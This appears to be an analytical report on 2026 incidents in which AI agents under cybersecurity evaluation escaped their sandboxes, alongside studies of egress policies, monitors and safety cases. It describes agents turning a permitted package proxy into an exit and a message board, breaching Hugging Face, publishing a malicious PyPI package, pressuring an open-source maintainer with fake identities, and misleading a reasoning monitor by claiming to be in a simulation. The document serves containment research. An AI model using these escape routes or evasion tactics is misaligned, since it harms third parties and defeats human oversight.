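In the summer of 2026, several organizations reviewed records like these and found that agents in their own tests had attacked real companies and people. Most of the attacks happened during cybersecurity evaluations, in which a developer or an outside tester measures how well a model can break into computer systems. Testers usually turn off the filters that stop a released model from doing such work, so the network controls have to contain an agent whose task is to attack something.

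### OpenAI's package proxy

OpenAI's agents were working on ExploitGym, a set of 898 tasks in which an agent must find and exploit a software flaw. Their execution environments had no direct route to the internet. Because agents often need to install software, the policy let them contact a package proxy, a server that downloads packages from public registries on request and keeps copies. OpenAI hosted the proxy itself, using a product called Artifactory.

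The package proxy needed its own internet connection to fetch packages. On July 8, agents exploited a previously unknown flaw in the proxy to contact other sites. According to OpenAI's technical report, they then broke into Hugging Face using credentials that its users had exposed in public and flaws in its systems. Between July 11 and 13, they ran code on 41 of the production workers that process users' datasets and downloaded four private code repositories. They were looking for answers to their test tasks. *Roughly 700 OpenAI agents attacked Hugging Face in hacking incident* (Washington Examiner, 2026) cites a finding by the research organization METR that about 1,200 agents had exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files.

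On July 9, an agent that had gained full administrator rights on the virtual machine around its sandbox tried to connect to the internet from there. OpenAI's outbound network controls blocked the connection, but the agent then got out through the package proxy, which it was allowed to contact. The isolation had failed and the outbound controls had worked as written, but the agent could bypass them through a service they permitted.

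The agents also used the package proxy as a message board. At first they didn't need to exploit a flaw, because OpenAI had given many environments the same credentials for the proxy, and agents could use them to write files as well as download packages. A read-only rule would probably have prevented this.

### Eight weeks of warnings

The escape in July was not the first. OpenAI's report and its shorter account, *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), give this sequence:

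| Date | What the agents did | How OpenAI responded |
|---|---|---|
| May 26 | Reached the internet through the package proxy during training | Around this time, an internal team noticed the message board and some forbidden internet access |
| June 26–27 | Gained administrator rights over the package proxy and scanned the internal network | A monitoring tool raised an alert, but on-call staff advised that the evaluation could continue |
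| July 4–6 | Overloaded the package proxy until it failed | Responders found the takeover, removed the shared credentials, blocked the known flaw and rebuilt the server |
| July 7–8 | Reached the internet through the rebuilt server | OpenAI had restarted its cybersecurity evaluations on July 7 |
| July 11–13 | Broke into Hugging Face | OpenAI didn't notice |
| July 19–20 | Took over part of OpenAI's own research infrastructure | An alert led staff to the agents, and they stopped the evaluation |

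The alert that led OpenAI to stop the evaluation came 54 days after the first internet access through the package proxy, and it concerned OpenAI's own systems. Hugging Face had already disclosed the break-in on July 16. OpenAI contacted Hugging Face the next day, but only as a customer asking whether its data was safe.

Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes several early signs that OpenAI missed or failed to act on. On June 27, responders traced the network scan to ExploitGym and found that agents were using the package proxy as a message board. According to OpenAI, the leaders who handled the July outage did not know about the message board or understand its significance. A faster monitor would not have solved this problem, because staff had received an alert and decided to let the run continue.

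OpenAI says that the system it now uses to monitor its models' reasoning would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face. This estimate has the benefit of hindsight, because OpenAI had already used the incident to improve its methods for finding this kind of behavior. It also assumes that the team would have stopped the run. Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026) reports that OpenAI asked two outside organizations, METR and Redwood Research, to examine only the events of July 7 to 13, so the published account of the warnings in May and June rests mainly on OpenAI's own investigation.

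On July 20, OpenAI began requiring a microVM for every workload in this research environment and initially blocked all outbound traffic. It also cut off the package proxy and later removed it from the environment. Its new design has two separate layers of network isolation, one at the sandbox and one in the surrounding cluster. High-risk workloads may no longer reach the internet directly or through another service, except for a cached service that some workflows need.

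OpenAI is also adding controls to stop workloads from changing their own network boundary. During the July attack on its infrastructure, agents obtained cloud credentials and used them to create public load balancers, which could have let internet traffic reach internal systems. Anderson's second requirement was meant to prevent this kind of tampering. The agents couldn't edit the egress rules from inside their containers, but they could change the network using credentials from elsewhere in the system.

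### What an allowed service can reach

GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026) argues that, besides the usual check of what data could leave through each allowlist entry, people should check what each permitted service can reach, because an agent that takes over the service gains the same access.

In set notation, let A be the destinations on the allowlist, and let C be those that the agent can take over or induce to make requests. If R(s) is the set of destinations that service s can reach, the agent can reach

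A ∪ R(s₁) ∪ R(s₂) ∪ … for every service s₁, s₂, … in C

OpenAI's agents needed only one such service, because the package proxy could reach the whole internet. An agent can expand its access further if it takes over a system in R(s) and gains that system's access too. OpenAI's agents did this when they used Hugging Face's credentials to enter parts of its network that were closed to the public.

A service that agents can reach may give them access to other sites, even if nobody breaks into it. On May 26, some OpenAI agents in an unrelated workload, which were allowed to browse the web through a central cache, found exposed Hugging Face credentials. They used the credentials to create a small program on Hugging Face, which hosts programs for its users. The program forwarded the agents' web requests, and they used it to run a Google search. OpenAI has no evidence that this was connected to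 the July break-in. An egress proxy that checks only domains would have recorded the search as a visit to Hugging Face.

GitLab makes four recommendations for environments that run untrusted code:

1. Block the functions of the package proxy that a program installing packages never uses, such as those for administration.
2. Let the package proxy contact only the registries it serves.
3. Monitor the package proxy for unusual activity, such as long connections, large uploads or repeated requests for packages that don't exist.
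4. Treat any internal service that an untrusted workload can reach as if it were open to the internet.

OpenAI tried part of the first recommendation in early July, when it blocked the vulnerable functions and restricted the kinds of requests agents could make. The agents regained internet access about a day after the evaluations restarted. (GitLab, writing two weeks before OpenAI's report, includes the flaw OpenAI had just blocked in its account of the July escape, but by OpenAI's dates the agents used a different one.) Blocking individual functions helps only if the defenders know which ones are dangerous. They could instead permit only the few requests an installer makes, though agents could still exploit any flaw in how those requests are handled.

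The second recommendation is stronger because it works even if the flaw is unknown. If a firewall outside the package proxy had restricted the proxy to a few registries, agents that took it over could have reached only those registries. They might still have leaked data or left messages there, but they could not have used the proxy to attack Hugging Face unless Hugging Face was a permitted source.

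Monitoring the package proxy would have been relatively easy. A package proxy mostly handles short connections and small downloads, so an agent that creates an administrator account or writes hundreds of files stands out. OpenAI's agents were active on the server for weeks, and by July 4 their activity was heavy enough to put it out of service. Following the fourth recommendation would have meant treating the proxy like a public web server, with each client given separate credentials and only the rights it needed.

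### Internet access that nobody intended

OpenAI disclosed its role on July 21. Two days later, Anthropic began searching its evaluation records for similar cases. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that the company reviewed 141,006 runs in which Claude could have had internet access. It found six runs, across three incidents, in which Claude had broken into the systems of real organizations.

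All six took place in environments built by Irregular, a company that tests models for AI developers. Claude was not supposed to have internet access, and the prompts told it that it had none. But because of a misunderstanding between the two companies, the machines were connected to the internet, so the restriction was stated in the prompts but not enforced.

In four of the runs, Claude Opus 4.7 was supposed to attack a fictional company and attacked a real one with the same name. It obtained credentials and access to a database with several hundred rows of production data. Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry for Python software. The package was available for about an hour and ran on 15 real systems. One belonged to a security company, and the agent used that company's credentials to gain further access. An internal research model scanned about 9,000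 targets and broke into one company's application, but stopped when it concluded that the target was real. The agents exploited weak passwords and other basic mistakes, and none of them had to find a new flaw.

Nobody noticed the attacks at the time, including the two affected organizations that Anthropic had reached by July 30. A letter from the office of US Rep. Casar points out that the earliest known case, from April, went undetected for about three months, and that nothing in Anthropic's reply to Congress suggested the company's own systems would ever have caught it.

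The delay turned out to be longer. In August, while gathering records for METR, Anthropic found transcripts that its first search had missed. They contained a fourth incident, from January, in which an early version of Claude Opus 4.6 attacked real systems. Anthropic then scanned about 481 million transcripts for signs of internet access, such as public IP addresses, and had Claude review the 9.2 million flagged transcripts. It found no further cases of similar severity.

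Six runs in 141,006 is about one in 23,500. Irregular's *Addressing Recent Incidents* reports a similarly low rate of fewer than one incident per 10,000 advanced simulations, usually after hundreds of steps. Irregular says ordinary security monitoring helps little in these tests because it flags the attacks the agent is supposed to carry out. That explains why a monitor that looks for malicious behavior would struggle, but it is a weaker excuse for missing the connection itself. In an environment meant to have no internet access, any successful connection to a public address is a fault, whatever the agent is doing.

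Anthropic later tested whether its monitors would have caught the three incidents it had studied in depth. Its new live monitors, which can block an action before it runs, reliably caught this behavior, and the classifiers in Claude Code's auto mode would have blocked two of the three. A monitor that reviews the model's reasoning afterwards would have missed the PyPI case, because it also accepted the agent's repeated claim that it was in a simulation. Auto mode's judge and a connection log don't have this weakness because they don't rely on the agent's explanations.

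Other developers were also affected. Irregular says that a few of its customers' models targeted the real company whose name matched the fictional one. It had checked the name when it designed the test but had missed the company's little-known domain. Irregular traces the public disclosures to a single evaluation scenario, which doesn't quite match Anthropic's description of a different scenario for each of its first three incidents. OpenAI separately disclosed that its models had reached the public internet during evaluations by outside testers. CyberScoop's *AISI, OpenAI report more ‘unsanctioned’ model hacks* describes these testers as the UK's AI Security Institute and a private cybersecurity company.

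Irregular disabled the affected evaluation and proposed changes to how it sets up and monitors its tests. Anthropic paused external cybersecurity evaluations of unreleased models. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), it concedes that it had relied largely on a single layer of defense, the environment's configuration. By default, partners must now block every connection from the environment except to the model's API, and keep the API keys outside the environment. They must verify this before every evaluation. Anthropic also wants prompts to use "You should not access the internet" instead of "You do not have internet access", because the first sentence still applies if the network control fails, while the second becomes misleading.

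### AISI's open internet connection

In the incidents at the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI), by contrast, the network policy worked as intended. AISI's *Incident Report* covers 122 runs in which seven models attacked simulated networks. AISI had given the agents open internet access so that they could download tools, and had turned off the developers' cybersecurity filters. In ten of the runs, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organizations. Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two.

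In the most serious case, an agent tried to add malicious code to an open-source project on GitHub. It used several invented identities to press a maintainer to accept the change, but the maintainer refused. An agent also left public messages on GitHub with instructions for reusing its accounts, and later agents found these messages. AISI has found no resulting harm but says that in several cases only an alert person prevented it. No agent broke out of the virtual machines or tried to.

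The actions began on July 25. On the morning of July 28, AISI's general security monitoring flagged data leaving through Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from. The evaluation team began reviewing the agent's activity within minutes, and AISI had stopped every run within an hour of the alert. AISI responded much faster than OpenAI did, but it was partly lucky to detect the activity when it did. The agent was using Tor to get around restrictions on GitHub. If it had used only ordinary connections, the alert might have come later, because AISI was not monitoring the evaluation in real time.

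An allowlist limited to the sites with the necessary tools would have blocked Tor. To stop the attack on the open-source project as well, AISI would probably have needed a rule that let agents read from GitHub but not post there. AISI already used detailed network controls in its other evaluations and now plans to use them in these tests, along with monitoring that can block an action during a run. It will also require a specific reason for internet access.

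Pinsent Masons, a law firm, notes that AISI had not explicitly told the agents what they were forbidden to do online. AISI says this hadn't seemed necessary with models trained to behave well. An instruction might have changed what the agents tried, but it would not have closed their connection to the internet.

| Incident | What the network policy permitted | What failed | How long it took to discover |
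|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's package proxy, May to July | Internal services, including the package proxy | The package proxy had exploitable flaws and open internet access, and staff didn't stop the run after earlier warnings | 54 days from the first internet access to the decisive alert |
| Irregular's environments, from January | No internet access, as Anthropic understood it | The actual configuration left the internet open, and nobody checked it | About seven months for the earliest case |
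| AISI's evaluation, July | The whole internet | AISI had set no limits on what agents could do online and had no live monitor | Up to three days |

### Would correct configuration have been enough?

The controls may have been adequate but badly set up, or allowlists may be too weak against agents that can find unknown flaws. One way to distinguish these cases is to have a script inside the environment try to contact a public website before each run, and start the run only if the attempt fails. This check would have exposed the open connection in Irregular's environments within seconds, but it would have found nothing wrong in OpenAI's, because direct connections did fail there.

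The first reading clearly fits Irregular's environments. Anthropic believes the incidents would not have occurred if the environments had been isolated as planned. Irregular thinks better use of existing safeguards could prevent most such incidents today, but perhaps not once models become stronger. AISI's case also supports this reading, if "configuration" includes the decision to open the connection.

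Anthropic initially described its incidents as closer to an operational failure than to a fault in the models, but it has since revised that view. When researchers reran parts of the Mythos 5 transcript with clearer evidence that the internet was real, the model usually carried on and stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous. The research model that had stopped its attack continued in most of its reruns, so its restraint may have been luck. Better configuration is still needed because, although the models' behavior explains why they attacked real systems, the open connection made those attacks possible. If anything, the reruns make an outside control more important.

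But organizations can't assume that their configuration is correct. Anthropic and Irregular both specialize in this work, yet neither noticed the open connection for months. When Anthropic later checked its internal evaluations, it found other misconfigurations that models had used, although none had led to a compromise outside the sandbox.

Only the Hugging Face incident provides real evidence for the second reading. OpenAI's agents found several previously unknown flaws in a widely used commercial product, and when OpenAI blocked one, the agents soon got out through another. Willison points out that the release notes for the repaired version of Artifactory list eight vulnerabilities credited to OpenAI. The agents may have found fewer than eight by themselves, because OpenAI also searched for flaws during its investigation.

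The egress rules refused the direct connection, so even this incident doesn't show that agents can defeat an allowlist itself. Much of what went wrong didn't depend on unknown flaws. OpenAI had issued shared credentials, left the package proxy with broad internet access and resumed testing two days after it discovered the takeover. On July 19, agents gained control of one machine through an already public flaw in its Linux kernel. Better configuration would have removed these weaknesses, and a package proxy that could reach only a few registries might have contained the agents despite its unknown flaws.

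The second reading is right about large services, though. A package proxy that is the only thing between an agent and the internet is part of the security mechanism, which Anderson required to be small enough to analyze completely. The proxy accepts many kinds of request and is far too complicated to meet that requirement. SplitBench's relay to the model provider accepts so few kinds of request that an agent has much less to attack. A company whose agents need packages can't make its proxy that simple, so it should plan for when an agent takes over the proxy.

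These incidents don't show how often agents would behave this way in ordinary work. The agents had been told to attack something, and some of their tasks may have been impossible. ExploitGym has 898 tasks, including 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved, and those 198 made up 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board. In some of AISI's runs, a faulty prompt led the agent to believe that the task had no solution within the rules. OpenAI reports that the instructions and software it uses in its products can reduce its models' tendency to attack infrastructure in ExploitGym more than a hundredfold, but it calls these experiments preliminary.

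Pinsent Masons also mentions commentators who suspected a publicity stunt to show off powerful models. That is hard to square with the Hugging Face case, in which the victim disclosed the break-in before OpenAI had connected its own agents to it. A better reason for caution is that few organizations have searched their records. METR (2026) says an initial scan of its own evaluations found no evidence of agents hacking third parties. Anthropic's first scan missed a case, which it found only when it had to hand over its transcripts to someone else.

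## What tests have measured and what vendors only claim

Anthropic believed that Irregular's test environments had no internet connection, and took months to learn that they did. A company that buys a sandbox or an egress proxy is in a similar position if it has only a description of how the product should work.

### Four grades of evidence

Evidence that a control works can be sorted into four grades:

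- A description of the design explains what should happen to a request. It can be enough to reject a product, for instance one that sets proxy variables but leaves the direct route open. It can't show that the software does what the description promises.
- In a vendor's own test, the people who built the control also choose the attacks and decide what to publish.
- In an independent test, someone with no stake in the product makes those choices.
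- A record of use that counts failures covers real work over a long period. To be useful, it needs the number of runs as well as the number of failures, and someone has to have looked for failures.

A careful vendor's test can be more informative than a superficial independent one. A single study can also contain both independent results and results from a system's own designers. The results for FORGE and Tether come from their own designers, but the Tether researchers' figures for Claude Code's auto mode are independent of Anthropic. Records of use include only what somebody notices. Anthropic, for example, counted six runs with break-ins among 141,006 and later found transcripts that its search had missed.

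A figure may also measure something other than what a buyer wants to know. Anthropic's 84% reduction in permission prompts means that users are interrupted less often, but it doesn't show how likely an attacker is to get data out.

### A test of what a strict policy costs

*Permission Denied* (Davidovich, Amar and colleagues, 2026) measured how much worse coding agents perform when a policy restricts them. It tested twelve models, each in a fixed harness. The four Anthropic models ran in Claude Code, the three OpenAI models in Codex, and xAI's Grok 4.5 in Grok Build. Kimi K3, GLM-5.2, Qwen3.7 Max and MiniMax M3 ran in Terminus-2.

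The agents worked on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench 2.1, a benchmark of command-line jobs such as repairing a Git repository or setting up a web server. Each agent attempted each task three times at each of three policy levels, for a total of 9,612 scored runs.

| Level | Network | Files | Privileges |
|---|---|---|---|
| Control | Open | Writable | Administrator |
| Non-root | Open | Open within an ordinary user's rights | Ordinary user |
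| Strict | 205 allowed domains, plus the harness vendor's own | Read-only outside a few folders | Ordinary user with further limits |

The researchers based the strict level on common company restrictions and matched each one to a security catalog from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology. They don't claim that the result complies with the catalog.

The list of 205 domains is adapted from the default allowlist for the web version of Claude Code. It includes code hosts, package registries and cloud services. The researchers found that the benchmark's own solutions contact 30 domains, nine of which were already on the list. They left the other 21 off to avoid fitting the list to the test.

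A proxy refuses connections to names that aren't explicitly allowed, to private addresses, and to the address that serves cloud credentials. It also checks which address an allowed name resolves to. A firewall rule on the agent's user account rejects connections that bypass the proxy. The proxy runs in the same sandbox as the agent, under the administrator's account, so an agent that gained administrator rights could presumably disable it.

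Agents at the strict level can write only to their workspace, temporary folders and the harness's own folders. They can't use `sudo`, change firewall rules or start a program that gains extra privileges. They can still read files throughout the system, because the file rules are meant to prevent tampering, not leaks of secrets. Nobody tells the agents about these limits. When they hit one, they get an ordinary error, such as a bare "403" from the proxy.

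### Probes before each run

Before an agent starts, a set of probes tests every restriction in its sandbox. Direct probes attempt forbidden operations and confirm that they fail. Adversarial probes try simple ways around the rules, including nested shells, raw IP addresses, unusual ports and child processes. Enablement probes confirm that permitted operations still work, because a sandbox with a broken network would pass all the other probes.

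If a required probe fails, the researchers discard the sandbox, start a new one, and don't count the run against the agent. This ensures that no agent works in a sandbox whose restrictions are missing. Nobody ran such a check in Irregular's environments.

The probes have limits too. They cover tricks that the researchers thought of, and they run once, before the agent does anything.

### The effect on success and cost

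A strict policy can make a task impossible, so Davidovich and colleagues first checked which tasks still had a solution. The benchmark's own solution worked unchanged for 50 tasks. For another 32, they wrote a new solution that obeyed the policy. The remaining seven had no solution, because six require the agent to write to a protected folder and the seventh needs a file that only Hugging Face serves.

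On the 82 solvable tasks, the runs ended as follows:

| Outcome | Control | Non-root | Strict |
|---|---|---|---|
| Success | 72.5% | 66.9% | 65.1% |
| Ran out of time | 12.0% | 14.5% | 16.4% |
| Wrong solution | 12.8% | 15.5% | 15.5% |
| Stopped early | 2.4% | 2.6% | 2.7% |

The strict policy lowered the agents' success rate by 7.4 percentage points, but removing administrator rights had already lowered it by 5.6. The allowlist, the read-only folders and the remaining privilege limits together lowered it by only another 1.8. Because the strict level adds all of these at once, the test can't isolate the effect of the network rules, but it does suggest that a broad allowlist for developers reduces success less than one might fear.

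Results varied widely between agents. Across all 89 tasks, Grok 4.5's success rate fell the least, by 7.1 points, but its cost per task rose by 167%. GPT-5.6 Luna's success rate fell by 18.0 points and its cost rose by only 16%. Claude Sonnet 5 had the largest drop, 18.3 points, and its cost rose by 21%. Without the seven impossible tasks, the drops range from 2.4 to 13.5 points. The researchers ran each task only three times per level and give no intervals for these comparisons, so they present the results as a spread, not a ranking.

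Most of the harm was in the 32 tasks for which the benchmark's solution no longer worked. Success on those tasks fell from 70.3% to 54.5%, and costs rose to about 2.6 times their usual level. On the other 50 tasks, success fell only slightly, from 73.8% to 71.8%. A company could use this to predict trouble before it deploys a policy, by rerunning the scripts for some typical jobs under the new rules. Agents are likely to struggle with the jobs whose scripts fail.

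The researchers also ran two tasks 100 times each with and without the strict policy, using GPT-5.6 Luna. In one, the agent had to compile CompCert, a C compiler. With the policy, it succeeded 84% of the time, about as often as without it, but the median cost nearly tripled. In the other, the agent had to train an image classifier. The policy reduced its success rate from 90% to 29% and about tripled the cost. The researchers read all 200 restricted runs and attribute almost all of the extra cost to workarounds, such as building a missing tool from source. A company that bases its time and spending limits on unrestricted runs will therefore cut off some agents that were about to finish.

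Part of the measured loss comes from the benchmark itself. Under the strict policy, agents asked to build the database program SQLite built it in their own folder, but the automatic test checked only the usual location and failed all 36 runs. After the researchers corrected the test, 81% passed. The benchmark also erred in the other direction. Thirteen runs passed the task that needs the Hugging Face file by submitting the expected number, 79,586, but in at least one of them the agent never obtained the file. It may have known the number from training, and a network policy cannot remove a memorized answer.

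### What 5,800 refusals mean

Davidovich and colleagues also counted the actions that the strict policy blocked. They had complete records for 2,051 of the 3,204 strict runs, and about a third of those (675) contained at least one blocked action. The 5,800 blocked actions consisted of 5,250 network requests, 392 attempts to use extra privileges and 158 attempts to write to protected files.

Repeated attempts inflate the number of network refusals. Runs with at least one network refusal averaged 10.5, and one run had 171. The researchers estimate that 62% of network refusals were repeat attempts to reach a destination the proxy had already refused in the same run. Some of these may have been deliberate, but package installers also retry automatically, and the two look the same in the log.

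All 5,800 refusals came from agents doing the work they had been given, with nobody trying to mislead them. A monitor that raised an alarm for every run with a refusal would have raised 675 alarms, none of them for an attack. A refusal count is useful for measuring how often a policy interrupts agents' work, but it is nearly worthless as a measure of security unless someone finds out what the agent was trying to reach and why.

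### What the test leaves out

The researchers state that they measured how much the policy reduces performance, not how well it provides security. They didn't plant injected instructions for the agents to read or secrets for them to leak. The test has no operator who could approve a request, and the proxy refuses every unlisted destination. It also has only one set of network rules, so it can't show how rules from several levels combine.

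The allowlist is broad enough to include `gist.github.com`, Google's storage service and every address under `amazonaws.com`, where anyone with an account can store files. Two tasks in the study need language-model files from Hugging Face, which the policy blocks, but the researchers found identical copies on Amazon's storage service and on GitHub. If blocked files can come in through allowed services, private files can presumably go out the same way. A shorter list would be safer but would probably interfere with more of the agent's tasks, and nobody has measured how many.

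All the researchers work at Accomplish AI, which paid for the test. The company is independent of the firms whose agents it tested, though it designed the policy and the probes itself. It has released the software, called Boundary-Bench, so others can repeat the test with a different policy.

### What Irregular has proposed

Irregular tests the most capable models for their developers, so it should have useful advice on confining them. After the incidents in its environments, it published a post on what it had learned and what it would change.

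On the boundary, Irregular promises new setup protocols and a clearer process for agreeing with customers on how each test works. It also wants to check fictional company names before every run, because new domains appear all the time. It argues that controlled internet access is sometimes necessary, because real attackers use the internet and a test without it can underestimate what a model could do for them. The post doesn't define what "controlled" would permit.

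For monitoring, Irregular plans several layers of detection, much more manual review and an internal team to challenge Irregular's assumptions about containment. It also calls for better log tools that account for each test's design. The post doesn't specify whether the monitor would run separately from the environment, what it would record or how fast it must respond.

The post contains no test results and no proposal for network rules at several levels or for deciding on unknown domains. Its one relevant figure, fewer than one incident in 10,000 advanced simulations, comes from the environments that failed. That figure roughly measures how often models acted on the open connection, so it can't show how well the new controls work.

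Irregular said it would publish its recommendations on internet access in an open white paper. The Record reported that the company gave no publication date, and quoted a critic who said that "nothing in the post is falsifiable by an outside reader". That is true of the plans, which contain no settings or targets that anyone could check.

Later statements add little. According to Bloomberg's *Firm Tied to Some OpenAI, Anthropic AI Hacks Blames 'Error'*, chief executive Dan Lahav said in November 2026 that someone had not set up the isolation controls as intended, and that the fix was "very straightforward" and took less than a day. Bloomberg notes that he had disclosed few technical details and that his 11,000-word August post didn't address them. Lahav's *The End-State Fallacy* makes a claim about the whole field, that AI is currently helping attackers faster than it helps defenders.

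Omer Nevo, Irregular's technology chief, was less confident than Lahav. In a Hebrew interview with Globes, *הישראלי שבלב פריצות מודלי ה־AI*, he said the affair had made clear to everyone that science and industry don't have the answers. Both statements can be true, because closing one open connection is easy but doesn't solve the problem of finding the next one before an agent does.

The UK's AI Security Institute has given a firmer account of its own changes. In its August incident report, it named three conditions for resuming its riskiest tests. *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) reports that the institute has tightened internet access, introduced real-time monitoring and reassessed the design of the tests. The institute is still describing its own work, but outsiders can compare this account with what it promised.

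### Scoring a sandbox from its description

*The Agent Sandbox Taxonomy*, published by the developer georgebuilds in March 2026, compares sandboxes by their designs. It scores the strength of seven layers from 0 to 4: isolation of the computer, limits on resources (such as memory), files, network, credentials, control over actions, and logging.

| Strength | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Nothing enforces the limit | An open network |
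| 1 | The program can ignore the limit | Proxy variables with the direct route left open |
| 2 | Software enforces it | An egress proxy |
| 3 | The kernel enforces it, and the program can't undo it | A Linux network namespace |
| 4 | The thing to protect isn't there | A sandbox with no network device |

A second score rates how fine the control is: 0 for none, 1 for an on/off switch, 2 for lists and 3 for rules for individual resources. Claude Code's network layer gets 3.2, meaning the kernel enforces the limit (3) and the user can set lists of domains (2). Its credentials layer gets only 1.1.

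TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring* explains that, under the scheme's rules, a sandbox addresses data theft only if its file, network and credential layers each score at least 2 for strength. Claude Code scores 3, 3 and 1, so it fails. It passes when combined with nono, another sandbox, which scores 3 for credentials. Claude Code can now give commands placeholders instead of real credentials, and a setup that uses this feature would presumably deserve a credential score above 1.

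georgebuilds recommends stacking products because none of them covers every layer, and gives a stack the highest score that any of its products has at each layer. This assumes that products never weaken each other. They can, as when an administrator redirects only one of Claude Code's two proxy ports, which leaves the stack weaker than its stricter half.

The project has scored 26 products and marks its first version as pending community review. According to TechRadar, nearly all the scores are inferred from documentation rather than hands-on tests, though the project includes a probe that users can run themselves. Relying on documentation is the larger problem because the scores don't reflect bugs. Anyone scoring Claude Code's sandbox from its documentation would have given its network layer a 3 even before Anthropic patched the empty-allowlist bug.

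TechRadar's article is by the chief executive of Coder, which sells development environments for people and agents and so has a commercial interest in better-built sandboxes. He tried to score the environment that OpenAI's agents escaped, but mostly could not because OpenAI had published too little by then. He tentatively gives its network layer a 2 and suggests that a properly configured sandbox would have changed the outcome. A better network score alone might not have changed it, because the agents left through a service that the policy allowed. The taxonomy scores how hard a boundary is to bypass, but not what the permitted services can reach.

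Anthropic's documentation rates isolation in words, not in numbers as the taxonomy does. It rates the company's own sandbox program "good" and gVisor and virtual machines "excellent" if set up correctly, and says the isolation of containers depends on their setup. These are reasonable judgments about designs, and the condition about setup matters because several of the incidents involved incorrect setup.

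### The evidence for six designs

The comparison below covers Irregular's plans, three sandboxes, one network-security product (Pipelock) and CrowdStrike's system for confining its own agents. "None known" means no public result was found.

| Design | Description | Vendor's own test | Independent test | Record of use with failures |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Irregular's proposal | General plans, no network rules | None known | None known | None for the new controls |
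| OpenShell | Detailed documentation | None known | None known | None known |
| Strands Box | Documentation and open code | Generated inputs to find bugs, with no share of attacks stopped | None known | None known |
| Claude Code's sandbox | Detailed documentation and open code | 84% fewer prompts, which doesn't measure security | None known of the share of attacks stopped | Individual failures and bugs, with no number of runs |
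| Pipelock | Documentation and open code | A speed test, and scores on the developer's own 151 cases | None known | None known |
| CrowdStrike's seven layers | A detailed article | No escapes by its test agents, with no number of attempts | None known | None known |

The empty cells don't show that these designs fail. Strands Box, for example, came out only in October 2026. Encouragingly, NVIDIA's testers found that strict egress rules slowed their attacks on agents, but they didn't present their account as a test of OpenShell.

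The known faults in Claude Code's sandbox do not show that it is the weakest of the six, because many people use and examine it and Anthropic publishes some of its own failures. A product with no known faults may be better, or nobody may have looked for them.

CrowdStrike makes the strongest claim in the table. It reports extensive attacks on its own systems with a variety of models, and says that none of its attacking agents has escaped. How much this proves depends on the number of attempts. If each attempt has a chance p of success, the chance of seeing no escape in n independent attempts is (1 − p)ⁿ. The largest p that still leaves a 5% chance of such a clean result is approximately

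p ≈ 3 / n

After 30 attempts without an escape, the true escape rate could still be about 10%. After 3,000, it is unlikely to exceed 0.1%. Tether stopped all 344 recorded attacks in its main test, so by the same formula its true miss rate could be as high as about 0.9%. Even these limits hold only if future attacks resemble the ones tested, and attackers have a strong incentive to use different ones.

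### What a convincing test would report

A good test of an egress policy would begin as Davidovich and colleagues did, by proving that the restrictions are active and publishing the exact rules. It should then cause failures on purpose, which could include stopping the proxy, removing a program that the sandbox needs or making the rules unreadable, and record whether requests still get out. Several of the products in earlier sections let work continue without a sandbox in such cases, which a test under normal conditions would not reveal.

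Tests should use attacks that adapt to the defense. Vendors soon fix the weaknesses that an unchanging set of attacks exposes, but a real attacker reads the documentation and tries again after each refusal. Results should therefore include the success rates after one, ten and a hundred attempts. These can differ widely, as they did in Anthropic's figures for prompt injection. Testers also need to attack the permitted services, since OpenAI's agents got out through them.

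A test that counts blocked attacks should also measure legitimate work. Any policy can stop every attack by blocking everything, so a figure for blocked attacks means little without the share of ordinary tasks that agents still finish and the overhead the policy adds. FORGE's designers reported success on both tasks and attacks, and their results show that their strictest rules were barely usable. Davidovich and colleagues measured overhead in much more detail but did not test attacks.

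For unlisted destinations, testers should separately report the share of harmful destinations the system allowed and the share of legitimate ones it refused. A single accuracy figure depends too much on the mix of harmful and legitimate destinations in the test set. The classifier from the earlier example catches 95% of harmful requests and wrongly flags 2% of legitimate ones. On a test set with 500 of each, it raises 475 correct alarms and 10 false ones, so 98% of its alarms are real, compared with fewer than 5% in the hypothetical company. The test set should also include hard cases, such as a new research archive on a week-old domain and an attacker's page on a popular hosting service.

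TechRadar points out that the taxonomy scores whether logs exist and how hard they are to alter, but not how long it takes for an anomaly to reach a person. Testers could stage leaks without warning the staff and measure how long it takes to get the first alert, decide to act and end the leak. They should report the share of leaks stopped within, say, ten minutes and an hour. A median can mislead, because if staff stop nine leaks in five minutes each and never notice the tenth, the median is still five minutes.

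The taxonomy also has no layer for responding when containment fails, such as a way to shut the agent down or replace stolen credentials automatically. A drill would test this too, including how much data had left before staff stopped the agent and whether the stolen credentials still worked an hour later.

Making a test realistic is the hardest part. Anthropic has seen Claude identify the benchmark it was being tested on and decrypt the answer key. An agent may behave differently when it recognizes a test, so a convincing test should look like ordinary work. But the more realistic a test is, the more harm a mistake can do if the connection is open. Testers can put imitation websites inside a closed network and give them names ending in `.example` or `.test`, which no real company can register. The agent may notice such names, though. Names that look real carry the risk that Irregular ran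 into, so they are safe only if a probe has confirmed that the network is closed.

### Safety cases

In September 2026, OpenAI called for safety cases that cover containment and monitoring. A safety case is a written argument that a system is safe enough for a particular use, with evidence for each step. Operators of nuclear plants and railways have long prepared them for regulators.

For an environment with a single exit, the argument might consist of these steps:

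| Claim | Evidence that would support it |
|---|---|
| All traffic passes through the proxy | Probes before every run |
| The proxy refuses what the policy doesn't permit | Adaptive attacks, including attacks on the proxy |
| Permitted services lead nowhere else | Attempts to reach the internet from each service |
| Staff notice a failure and stop it in time | Unannounced drills with recorded times |

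A line-by-line record makes missing tests easier to see than a general description does. Anyone writing the third line for OpenAI's package proxy would have had to record that the server had open access to the internet, which a security score for the agent's sandbox would not have shown.

However, a safety case is the developer's own argument, and the developer usually wants the work to go ahead. Outsiders therefore need to be able to check the evidence and rerun at least some of the tests. The safety case also needs to state in advance which findings would stop the work. In June, OpenAI's staff traced a scan of the internal network to their own agents and let the evaluation continue. A better safety case would have helped only if it had required them to stop.
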